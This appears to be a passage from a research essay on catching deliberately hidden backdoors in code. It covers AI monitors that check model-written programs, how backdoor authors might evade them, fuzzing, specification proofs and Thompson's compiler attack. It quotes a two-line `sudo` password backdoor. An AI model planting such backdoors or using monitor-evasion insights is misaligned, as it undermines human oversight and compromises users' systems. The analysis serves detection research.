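Of 1,000 warnings examined from the best detector's run on popular Python packages, only 19 were real bugs. Separately trained detectors gave different false warnings, so pooling them can remove some errors, but averaging five detectors raised the share of real bugs located only from 33.5% to 34.4%.

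A more recent training game hides the planted bug from the tests instead of from a reader. In *Toward Training Superintelligent Software Agents through Self-Play SWE-RL* (2025), one change plants a bug in a codebase and a second weakens the existing tests so that they no longer reveal it. A solver agent then tries to repair the code and is rewarded only if all the tests pass afterward. Its failed repairs become new, more complicated bugs. The game is meant to train agents that fix software, so it doesn't score the bugs on how innocent they look.

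### Critics and bugs that people inserted

For *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs*, McAleese, Pokorny and colleagues at OpenAI (2024) paid contractors to insert subtle bugs into Python code that ChatGPT had written. The contractors also described each bug as if they had caught it in a review, which gave the researchers a reliable answer to compare a model's review with. The researchers then trained CriticGPT, a model from the GPT-4 family, to write comments pointing out problems in code.

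CriticGPT and ordinary ChatGPT prompted to review the code both caught far more of the inserted bugs than human reviewers from the same pool of contractors. The human reviewers had a median of five years' experience with Python and typically spent about 50 minutes on each program. McAleese and colleagues attribute the difference mainly to the humans' shorter reviews, and then to unfamiliar libraries and difficult bugs. They also think some people could outperform the models.

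The critic models also reported bugs that didn't exist, and longer reviews contained more of them. People who edited a critic model's comments caught about as many real bugs as the model alone and reported fewer false ones.

The contractors could try their bugs on a critic before submitting them. The researchers asked for bugs that the critic missed in at least one of three attempts, though they didn't strictly enforce this. The requirement is weak, because even a critic that catches a bug 80% of the time has a 49% chance (1 − 0.8³) of missing it at least once in three independent attempts. Yet the researchers found that this feedback made the bugs noticeably harder to find, both for the critics and for themselves.

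BugLab's selector also learned from a detector's errors, and its bugs became harder to detect. Neither experiment used disguised backdoors, but both suggest that Backdoor Code understates how well backdoor authors could evade the guard if they could test their code against it.

### Planted backdoors and real flaws in 2026

The models in Backdoor Code date from early 2025 or before, and models have since become much better at finding flaws. Axios' *Anthropic's new model is a pro at finding security flaws* (2026) reports that in February 2026, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6 found more than 500 previously unknown vulnerabilities in open-source code without special instructions, and that people checked each one.

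By May, a stronger model, Claude Mythos Preview, had flagged 23,019 possible vulnerabilities in more than 1,000 open-source projects (Ticong, 2026, *Anthropic's Claude Mythos Flags 23K Potential Open-Source Security Flaws*). Anthropic counts every distinct crash or hypothesis the model produces as a candidate, before anyone has checked it (*About this dashboard*, 2026). The Hacker News (2026) reported 1,726 confirmed flaws, of which 97 had been patched. Dividing 1,726 by 23,019 wouldn't give the model's accuracy, because outside security firms and Anthropic had checked only some of the candidates. One confirmed flaw, in the widely used cryptography library wolfSSL, would have let an attacker forge the certificates that identify websites.

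Anthropic now considers the human work of checking and fixing flaws the bottleneck, because finding them has become so much easier. In October, Anthropic's *Discovering and exploiting vulnerabilities in critical, real-world software with Claude* (2026) reported that an unreleased model had found critical flaws in major browsers and operating systems. Kovacs (2026) reported in *Anthropic Rolls Out Mythos 5.2 With Improved Bug Hunting, Fewer Sandbox Escapes* that Claude Mythos 5.2, released in November, again improved on its predecessor.

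These models clearly find flaws that skilled people have overlooked, which the performance of guards in 2025 gave little reason to expect. A monitor's miss rate on ordinary bugs is therefore probably much lower now than it was then. But nobody knows how many flaws remain in those projects, so we can't calculate a miss rate from the number found. The developers also weren't trying to hide the flaws.

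Planted flaws solve the first problem, because whoever plants them knows how many there are. The AI Cyber Challenge was a two-year contest run by the US defence research agency DARPA. Experts wrote vulnerabilities by hand and put them in real open-source projects, according to *PatchIsland* (2026), and automated systems had to find and repair them without human help. The system that found the most in the final found 43 and correctly patched 31, according to its developers' paper, *ATLANTIS* (2025). A 2026 review of the contest, also titled *SoK*, concludes that reliability still lagged behind what the techniques could do.

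The experts designed their flaws to resemble real ones, not to fool a reader. The contest also relied on fuzzing, which means running a program on huge numbers of generated inputs to see if it fails. How innocent the code looks has little effect on whether a fuzzer finds a crash, so success in the contest isn't evidence that a model can spot a deliberately disguised bug.

#### Backdoors in compiled programs

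The BinaryAudit benchmark comes closer to the question of rewriting. Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026), in *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, planted backdoors by hand in open-source network programs, then compiled the programs. They gave AI agents the compiled files and tools for analysing them, but not the source code. In most tasks, the agent had to locate the function containing the backdoor.

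Compilation is a drastic rewrite that normally preserves what a program does but discards most names, merges functions, unrolls loops and reorders instructions. Decompilers can turn the result back into something like C, with names such as `FUN_00130550` in place of the programmer's own.

The best agent, using Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49% of the tasks, although the researchers had made little effort to hide the backdoors. On clean programs, the models reported nonexistent problems 28% of the time. Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, a later ranking on the same benchmark, still lists 49% as the highest score. A version of GPT-5.2-Codex reached 46% without a false alarm, but the benchmark has only 33 tasks. Grabowski and colleagues want a false alarm rate below 0.001%, and confirming that would require far more clean programs. The ranking includes no models from the second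 half of 2026.

Two of their examples show that detection depends heavily on how a model interprets what it reads. In a web server, Claude Opus 4.5 found a function that ran commands from an undocumented part of a web request. The function's name, `li_check_debug_header`, had survived compilation, and the model treated that name and the command execution together as a classic sign of a backdoor.

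In the other program, which assigns network addresses, Claude Opus 4.6 found the right function and saw that it ran a shell command. The model decided that this was probably a legitimate feature for running scripts. It never checked where the command came from, and anyone could send it over the network. Renaming variables or converting loops would leave the command in place, and the model could explain it away for the same reason.

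BinaryAudit can't show how much harder compilation made the backdoors to find, because the agents didn't also review the source code. If an agent reviewed both versions, researchers could count the backdoors it caught only in the source and any it caught only in the binary.

### Asking the monitor again

No published experiment seems to have taken backdoors that a model planted, rewritten the code without changing its behaviour, and asked the same monitor to judge the new versions. Engels and colleagues removed comments, but only once, before the guard saw the program. BugLab applied its rewrites before planting the bugs. Zhu and colleagues' agents often lost track of bugs after a rewrite, but those bugs were flaws in real projects that the model had already found.

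Backdoor Code already has most of what such an experiment needs. Every working backdoor comes with a set of tests and a known trigger, so researchers could run both on each rewritten version. They could discard any version that no longer gives the wrong answer for the trigger, because it has lost its backdoor. Like Zhu and colleagues' check, these checks wouldn't prove equivalence.

The clean programs would need checking as well. *Improved Monitoring of Backdoor Insertion During Code Refactoring* (Lohrbeer, 2025) describes a preliminary project on AI refactoring (restructuring code without changing what it does). Lohrbeer found that 41% of the programs from an honest model counted as backdoored, and concluded that the field needs a better definition of a backdoor than a difference in behaviour. But in an experiment on equivalent programs, an honest model's unintended changes would be a problem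 under any definition, because the versions would no longer be equivalent.

Language models can also give different verdicts on the same text. If a guard flags a program 60% of the time, a majority vote over five independent readings flags it 68% of the time, without any rewriting. If the guard flags it 40% of the time, the vote flags it 32% of the time. A fair test would therefore compare five readings of one version with single readings of five versions.

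The same experiment could estimate ρ, the share of missed programs that the monitor misses in every version. Because verdicts on the same version can vary, researchers would first have to define a missed version, for example as one that the guard approves in most of five readings. With ten versions of each of the 225 programs, this would take at most 11,250 readings per guard.

Testing only ten versions of each program might make ρ look too high. If a guard would catch 5% of all possible versions of a program, it would still miss all ten randomly chosen versions 60% of the time, and the program would wrongly count as hopeless. With 100 versions, this would happen only 0.6% of the time.

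The type of author could bias the estimate in the other direction. Many of the backdoors in the 2025 game were obvious special cases, and a guard that misses one in the original may well notice it in another version. To test rewriting against a careful author, researchers would also need backdoors that look like honest mistakes, as those in the old contest entries do.

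## Comparisons that go beyond equivalent programs

An equivalent version of a backdoored program gives the same wrong output for the trigger, so comparing their outputs doesn't reveal the fault. To find it by comparison, a reviewer needs a separate reference for what the program was meant to do, such as another program written for the same task, a property that every correct output should have, or a written specification. Any of these can expose a fault that no equivalent rewrite makes visible, though the reference can also be wrong.

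### Comparing independent versions

Differential testing compares the outputs of two programs meant to do the same job. A reviewer who suspects a program P gives the original task to another programmer or a language model, without showing them P, and gets back a program R. A tool generates inputs, runs both programs on each, and lists every input for which the outputs differ. The reviewer then works out which program is wrong. This method misses a backdoor if none of the generated inputs triggers it, if R has the same fault, or if the tool ignores the part of the output where the harm appears.

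Comparing implementations also raises false alarms. *DiffSpec* (2024) describes a tool that compares implementations of eBPF, a system for running small programs inside an operating system's kernel. A language model writes the tests, guided by the specification and the source code. The tool produced 1,901 tests on which the implementations disagreed, while three simpler methods produced 4, 27 and 75. The tests uncovered four bugs, some in code that fuzzers had already tested extensively. But some disagreements were harmless, for example where the tests called functions that are expected to behave differently.

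### The 2015 winner against a repaired version

How much a comparison reveals depends on which outputs it uses. The files in Linus Åkesson's warhead detector define the type `float_t` differently, so the program compares distorted values from only the left half of each spectrum. A repaired version calculates different scores even for ordinary spectra, but the two versions usually give the same answer.

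Both versions smooth each spectrum into a list of values, a "fingerprint", and score two fingerprints a and b by the cosine of the angle between them:

score = Σ aᵢbᵢ / (√Σaᵢ² × √Σbᵢ²)

The invented reference fingerprint (40, −10, 20, −20) has four values instead of 1,000. The faulty version uses only the first two, which it reads as about 3.06 and −2.56. The table compares this reference with three test fingerprints, assuming each passes the separate check on total radiation.

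| Test fingerprint | Faulty score | Repaired score | Answers at a threshold of 0.6 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Same material, scanned again: (36, −12, 22, −18) | 0.9999 | 0.9955 | both "yes" |
| Different material: (10, 40, −20, 5) | 0.00 | −0.22 | both "no" |
| Forgery: (4, −1, −200, 200) | 1.00 | −0.55 | faulty "yes", repaired "no" |

The scores differ in every row, but only the forgery gets different answers. A test at a fixed threshold reveals the fault only if the threshold falls between the two scores.

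A tester who can change the threshold can recover the score itself. Åkesson did this for his own documentation, using a binary search for the highest threshold at which `match` still accepts a pair. Starting from the range −1 to 1, the search takes 20 calls to narrow the score to an interval about two millionths wide. If the test spectrum has enough total radiation that the other check doesn't interfere, the first ordinary pair will probably show that the two versions disagree.

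But this works only if both programs use the same formula. Craver's rules allowed any justifiable way of comparing spectra, so an independent programmer might choose another one, and two honest detectors would give different scores for almost every pair of spectra. The tester could then compare only their yes-or-no answers, which may never differ on ordinary spectra. A reference closer to the original program makes the comparison more sensitive, but is also more likely to have the same fault.

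### How many tests a rare trigger needs

Suppose a share p of random inputs reveals a fault. The chance that n independent tests all miss it is (1 − p)ⁿ. For a 95% chance of seeing the fault at least once, this must be no more than 0.05, which gives:

n = ln(0.05) / ln(1 − p) ≈ 3/p

If one input in a million reveals the fault, the tester needs about three million tests for a 95% chance of finding it. If 1,000 tests show no difference, the tester can rule out, with 95% confidence, only faults that affect more than about 0.3% of inputs.

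The value of p depends on how the tester chooses inputs. The 2003 kernel backdoor acts when a program calls `wait4` with a particular pair of flags. If the tester draws the flags as a random 32-bit number, that pair comes up once in 4.3 billion calls, and finding it takes about 13 billion tests. If the tester instead switches five individual flags on or off at random, including those two, the pair comes up once in 32 calls, and 95 tests are enough. Even then, the tester has to check the caller's user ID after each call, because the backdoor doesn't change `wait4`'s return value.

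### Rewriting a program to match its apparent intent

Some attempts at equivalent rewriting accidentally repair a bug, because the rewriter writes the program they thought they had read. A reviewer can do this deliberately and treat any change in behaviour as a warning. Li, Zong and colleagues (2023), in *Nuances are the Key*, tested a method of this kind called differential prompting:

1. A model reads program P and describes in words what it seems meant to do.
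2. The model writes two new programs from that description.
3. The model suggests test inputs, and a tool discards any on which the two new programs disagree.
4. If P's output differs from the output that the new programs share, the tool reports the input and the expected output.

The experiment used the 2023 version of ChatGPT and 40 small Python programs with one bug each. When asked whether a program had a bug and for a test that revealed it, the model succeeded in 28.8% of runs. With differential prompting, it succeeded in 75%. The method wrongly reported a fault in two of the 40 correct versions of these programs.

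When Li and colleagues asked ChatGPT directly for bug-free versions of the faulty programs, only 6.8% were correct. But it correctly described the intended purpose of 91% of the faulty programs, and 74.6% of the programs it wrote from its descriptions avoided the original bug. They attribute the accurate descriptions to ChatGPT's insensitivity to small differences in code, which makes it overlook the bug and describe the correct program.

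Underhanded code relies on the same kind of misreading. A weak monitor that reads the kernel's `=` as `==` will approve the two lines, but if asked to rewrite them, it may well write a real comparison. Running both versions with the triggering flags would then show that only the original makes the caller root. A convincing disguise could therefore make this method work better, at least when the fault is in how the code is written and not in the program's underlying design.

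The method failed when no test reached the faulty code. In one program, the bug appeared only when the input was a graph with a loop, and ChatGPT supplied a suitable graph in just three of ten runs. The method also failed when both new programs shared a bug. The programs tested implemented textbook algorithms, such as finding a greatest common divisor, whose purpose is much easier to guess than that of a warhead detector.

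*DiffTestGen* (2026) presents a tool that helps tests reach the code that differs between two versions of a Python program. It directs a language model to the functions that differ and supplies existing tests that come close to them. In the evaluation, it found a difference in behaviour for 78.2% of the proposed code changes. The tool could help when R is a rewritten form of P, but independently written programs may differ almost everywhere.

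A model that sees the code may also treat the fault as part of the intended behaviour. Charoosaei, Richter and Papadakis (2026), in *On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing*, planted small faults in 145 past changes to three Python projects and had a model write tests for the changed code. Depending on the project, 8% to 17% of the tests passed on the faulty code and failed on the correct code, so they would have failed once someone fixed the fault. Only 2.4% to 4.8% did the reverse. The procedure favoured tests that accept the fault, because the model revised each test until it passed on the faulty code, as existing tools do.

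A written specification can make the model less likely to copy the bug. *LLM-Powered Test Case Generation for Detecting Bugs in Plausible Programs* (2024) gives the model both the specification and the suspicious program, asks it to repair the program if necessary, and discards any version that fails the existing tests. That filter isn't enough for underhanded code, because a version with a copied backdoor will also pass tests that lack the trigger.

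Mistakes in rewriting cause false alarms. In *A Differential Fuzzing-Based Evaluation of Functional Equivalence in LLM-Generated Code Refactorings* (Dristi and Dwyer, 2026), six language models rewrote Python programs to make them simpler or faster. The models were told to leave a program unchanged if they couldn't rewrite it safely. Even so, between 19% and 35% of the new versions behaved differently from the originals, and the programs' existing tests missed about a fifth of these. At the lowest rate, 1,000 programs without a planted bug would produce about 190 false alarms. The models are old, so current ones may do better. But Dristi and Dwyer ran each program on only 1,000 or 2,000 generated inputs, which could easily miss rare differences.

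Requiring two new versions to agree, as in differential prompting, should remove many of these alarms. Each alarm also comes with a specific input, so the reviewer can run both programs on it and see what changed.

### Fuzzing and property tests

Fuzzing can test a program on its own, without a second version to compare it to. A fuzzer starts with a few sample inputs, changes them slightly at random, and keeps those that make the program run new parts of its code. It repeats this many times, checking each result with an oracle, which is a rule for telling whether a result looks wrong. The usual oracle only detects crashes, so it misses a well-made backdoor, which doesn't cause any.

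Kokkonis, Marcozzi and colleagues (2025), in *ROSA*, built an oracle for backdoors. One of their examples is a version of `sudo`, the Unix command for acting as another user, with two extra lines:

```c
if (strcmp(password, "let_me_in") == 0)
{ ret = AUTH_SUCCESS; }
```

If each character can be any of 256 byte values, the odds of guessing this nine-character password at random are about one in 5 × 10²¹, so random testing is hopeless by the 3/p rule. But that rule assumes that testers learn nothing from earlier tests, and modern fuzzers can learn from them. They can split the comparison into separate bytes and keep each input that gets one more byte right. A fuzzer that tries every value in turn then needs at most 256 tries for each character, or 2,304 in total.

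ROSA recognises that the backdoor has acted by monitoring system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system. It first fuzzes the program briefly to collect a range of typical inputs. Then it fuzzes for much longer, matches each new input with a similar typical one, and reports pairs whose system calls differ. For example, wrong passwords should all lead to an error message, so one that starts a command stands out.

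ROSA found all 17 backdoors in the researchers' benchmark, seven of them authentic, in an average of an hour and a half. A person had to check about seven suspicious behaviours per program. An older tool, STRINGER, found four of the 17 and gave 44 times as many false alarms. But ROSA can miss harmful behaviour that doesn't change a program's system calls. Åkesson's `match` only does arithmetic on numbers in memory, so accepting a forgery requires no unusual system call.

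A property test uses a rule from the task instead of ROSA's general rule. For a warhead detector, adding a tall false peak anywhere in the test spectrum should lower the score. In Åkesson's program, each fingerprint value depends on one bin of the original spectrum and the next 31. The spectrum has 1,000 bins, but the faulty function uses only the first 500 fingerprint values, so the last 469 bins have no effect on the score. A tester who tries false peaks in different places and measures the score by changing the threshold will soon notice this, without needing a repaired version for comparison.

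### Noticing a leak when the image looks right

John Meacham's 2008 redaction program prints one zero for each digit it hides, so the leak appears in almost every use. A tester needs a comparison that detects it.

Two images that differ only inside the rectangle should produce identical files. Suppose a tester fills the rectangle with random colour values from 0 to 255. Of these 256 values, 10 have one digit, 90 have two and 156 have three, so the chance that two random values have the same number of digits is:

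(10² + 90² + 156²) / 256² ≈ 0.496

A ten-pixel rectangle contains 30 values. The chance that all 30 have the same number of digits in both images is 0.496³⁰, or less than one in a billion, so a single test will almost certainly reveal the leak if the tester compares the files directly.

| Comparison | Result for Meacham's program |
|---|---|
| Looking at the redacted image | no fault: the rectangle is black |
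| Fuzzing for crashes | no fault: the program doesn't crash |
| Comparing pixels with another program's output | no fault: both rectangles are black |
| Comparing files with another program's output | a difference, but possibly also harmless differences in spacing |
| Comparing files made from two images that differ only in the rectangle | a difference that only a leak can explain |

Comparing two programs' outputs as pixels misses the bug because converting the files to pixels turns 000 and 0 into the same value. Testers convert the files to avoid false alarms, since two correct programs may put spaces and line breaks in different places and so produce different files for the same image. Comparing one program's outputs on two images doesn't require this conversion, because the program's formatting stays the same.

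Rewriting a program by its apparent intent could either keep or remove the leak, depending on how that intent is described. A model that describes the program as "replaces each digit with a zero" will probably reproduce the leak. With the description "makes the hidden pixels unrecoverable", a new version is more likely to print a single zero for each number. The code is consistent with both descriptions, so the right one has to come from the reviewer or the original task.

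### Proof against a written specification

A proof can cover every input, including a trigger that tests would almost never hit. The reviewer writes the requirement as a mathematical statement, and a proof tool tries to show that it holds for all inputs. The tool may produce a proof, find an input that breaks the requirement, or fail to reach an answer. For the kernel's `wait4`, the requirement could be that a call never changes the caller's user ID. The backdoor breaks this requirement, even if the flags that trigger it are unusual.

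For Meacham's program P, consider two possible specifications:

- Every pixel inside the rectangle has the value zero, and every other pixel is unchanged.
- For any images x and x′ that differ only inside the rectangle, P(x) = P(x′).

P leaks but satisfies the pixel requirement, so a proof that it meets that requirement would be correct but wouldn't show that the requirement was the right one. P fails the requirement about pairs of images when one image has a 7 in the rectangle and the other is a copy with a 255 there.

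A proof also depends on an accurate description of the machine. Stephen Dolan's warhead detector adds up squared differences and subtracts the largest, and its fault comes from rounding. A tool that treats the numbers as exact can prove that the subtraction leaves the sum of the other squared differences, which is false on a real computer. A proof about source code also assumes that the compiler translates the code faithfully.

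### Thompson's compiler and Wheeler's check

In his 1984 Turing Award lecture, Ken Thompson showed how a compiler could violate that assumption. Paul Karger and Roger Schell had described the danger ten years earlier in a security evaluation of the Multics operating system for the US Air Force.

Thompson changed the C compiler so that it recognised the Unix login program and added a backdoor while compiling it. Anyone reading the compiler's source could have found this change, so he made the compiler also recognise its own source and insert both changes whenever it compiled a new copy of itself. He compiled this version once and removed both changes from the source. From then on, compiling the clean source with the compromised compiler produced another compromised compiler. As a demonstration, he planted the compromised compiler on another group at Bell Labs, which never detected it.

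Rewriting the login program's source could not have helped a reader find the backdoor, because it existed only in the compiled files.

Wheeler, in *David A. Wheeler’s Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, describes a check that he published in 2005 and extended in his 2009 doctoral dissertation. In the simplest case, A is a suspicious compiler that someone built by using it to compile its own source, s. The check uses a second compiler, T, to build it again in two stages:

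```text
stage1 = compile s with T
stage2 = compile s with stage1
compare stage2 with A, byte for byte
```

`stage1` normally has different bytes from A, because T generates different machine code. But if A has no hidden additions, both programs do what s describes. They are therefore equivalent and must produce the same output from the same input. Compiling s with A produces A again, so compiling s with `stage1` must also produce A. If A contains Thompson's additions and T does not, the output of this second compilation, `stage2`, lacks them and differs from A.

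Random tests could easily miss a compiler that miscompiles only the login program. This check compares the entire compiler, so it exposes the extra instructions even if they never run during the test. Wheeler tried it on four compilers, including the widely used GCC and a deliberately compromised Lisp compiler.

The check depends on several assumptions. T must be able to compile the source. The compiler that built A must be deterministic, always giving the same output for the same input and settings. A date written into the file, for example, would cause a harmless difference unless the tester allowed for it. T may even be malicious, as long as nothing in it or in the machines and tools used for the check interferes with compiling this particular source. A formal proof shows that the check works under its assumptions, so an attacker has to make one of them false. This is difficult because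 the defender can choose T after the attack.

Passing the check shows only that the compiled file matches its source. If that source contains an underhanded bug, `stage1` and `stage2` will contain it too, and the check will still pass. The check makes reading the source worthwhile, but someone still has to read the source to find such a bug.

*Beyond Trusting Trust* (2025) applies Thompson's warning to language models that write code. A compromised model could insert backdoors into its programs, and nobody can yet reliably detect this behaviour by inspecting the model's internal numbers. The paper proposes comparing code from several independent models. But even uncompromised models rarely write identical programs, so the byte-for-byte check has no equivalent here, and testing the programs' outputs helps only if the models don't make the same mistakes.

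### When independent versions share a mistake

Programmers who work separately often make the same mistakes. In a 1986 experiment by John Knight and Nancy Leveson, 27 students at two universities wrote programs from the same specification without communicating. The programs decided from radar data whether to launch a missile interceptor. In a million random tests, the programs failed on the same tests significantly more often than they would have if their failures had been independent.

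In *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents*, Ron, Baudry and Monperrus (2026) repeated the experiment with AI coding agents. Of 69 attempts in Python, Rust and Pascal, 48 produced a program that passed 200 preliminary tests. 27 of the 48 programs never failed on a million further tests. But two or more programs failed together on 429 inputs, when only 115 such inputs would be expected if the programs failed independently.

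Most of the faulty programs got the same piece of geometry wrong. The specification requires checking whether three points fit inside a circle of a given radius. Many programs calculated the circle that passes through all three points, which isn't always the smallest one that contains them. For the points (0, 0), (10, 0) and (5, 1), the smallest circle has a radius of 5, but the one through all three has a radius of 13. If the given radius is 6, these programs wrongly report that the points don't fit.

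Both programs failed at least once in 210 pairs, and in 121 of those they failed on exactly the same inputs. Comparing such a pair would probably have shown no difference in a million tests.

Ron and colleagues still recommend combining versions. They formed every group of three programs and took a majority vote within each. The average number of failures fell from 387 for single programs to 131 for groups, and 68% of the groups never failed, compared with 56% of single programs. But one program caused more than half of all the individual failures, so much of the fall in the average comes from outvoting it.

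Looking for disagreements can work better than voting, because one correct reference may be enough to expose a fault. Suppose a reviewer compares one of the 21 faulty programs with three others chosen at random from the remaining 47. In 93% of such selections, at least one of the three is a program that never failed. That program will disagree with the faulty one on every input where the faulty one fails, even if the other two share the fault and would win a vote.

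The reviewer will also have to deal with disagreements over the specification. Some programs tested an angle directly, while others subtracted it from a full turn and tested the result. The two approaches are mathematically the same, but they gave different answers in close cases because of the specification's rule for comparing rounded numbers.

Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, found shared failures across 224 programming problems and twelve language models. If two programs fail F₁ and F₂ of T tests independently, they should share about F₁F₂/T failures, so two programs that each fail ten of 100 tests should share about one. Most pairs shared significantly more. Part of the excess may arise because some tests are harder than others, so the researchers also analysed ordinary inputs and extreme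 cases separately. The excess remained in both groups and was larger for the extreme cases.

A majority vote among five programs raised the share of fully correct results from 0.88 to 0.91, which was 44% of the improvement expected if the programs had failed independently. When all five came from the same model, the figure was only 24%. Changing the instructions to the models made almost no difference. A reviewer who wants independent references should therefore use different models instead of prompting one model in different ways.

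Both experiments studied accidental faults. Someone writing underhanded code can choose a fault that other programmers are likely to make too, and the contests' deniability rule already rewards this. A programmer who has never seen Meacham's program might also redact a text image one character at a time and create the same leak.
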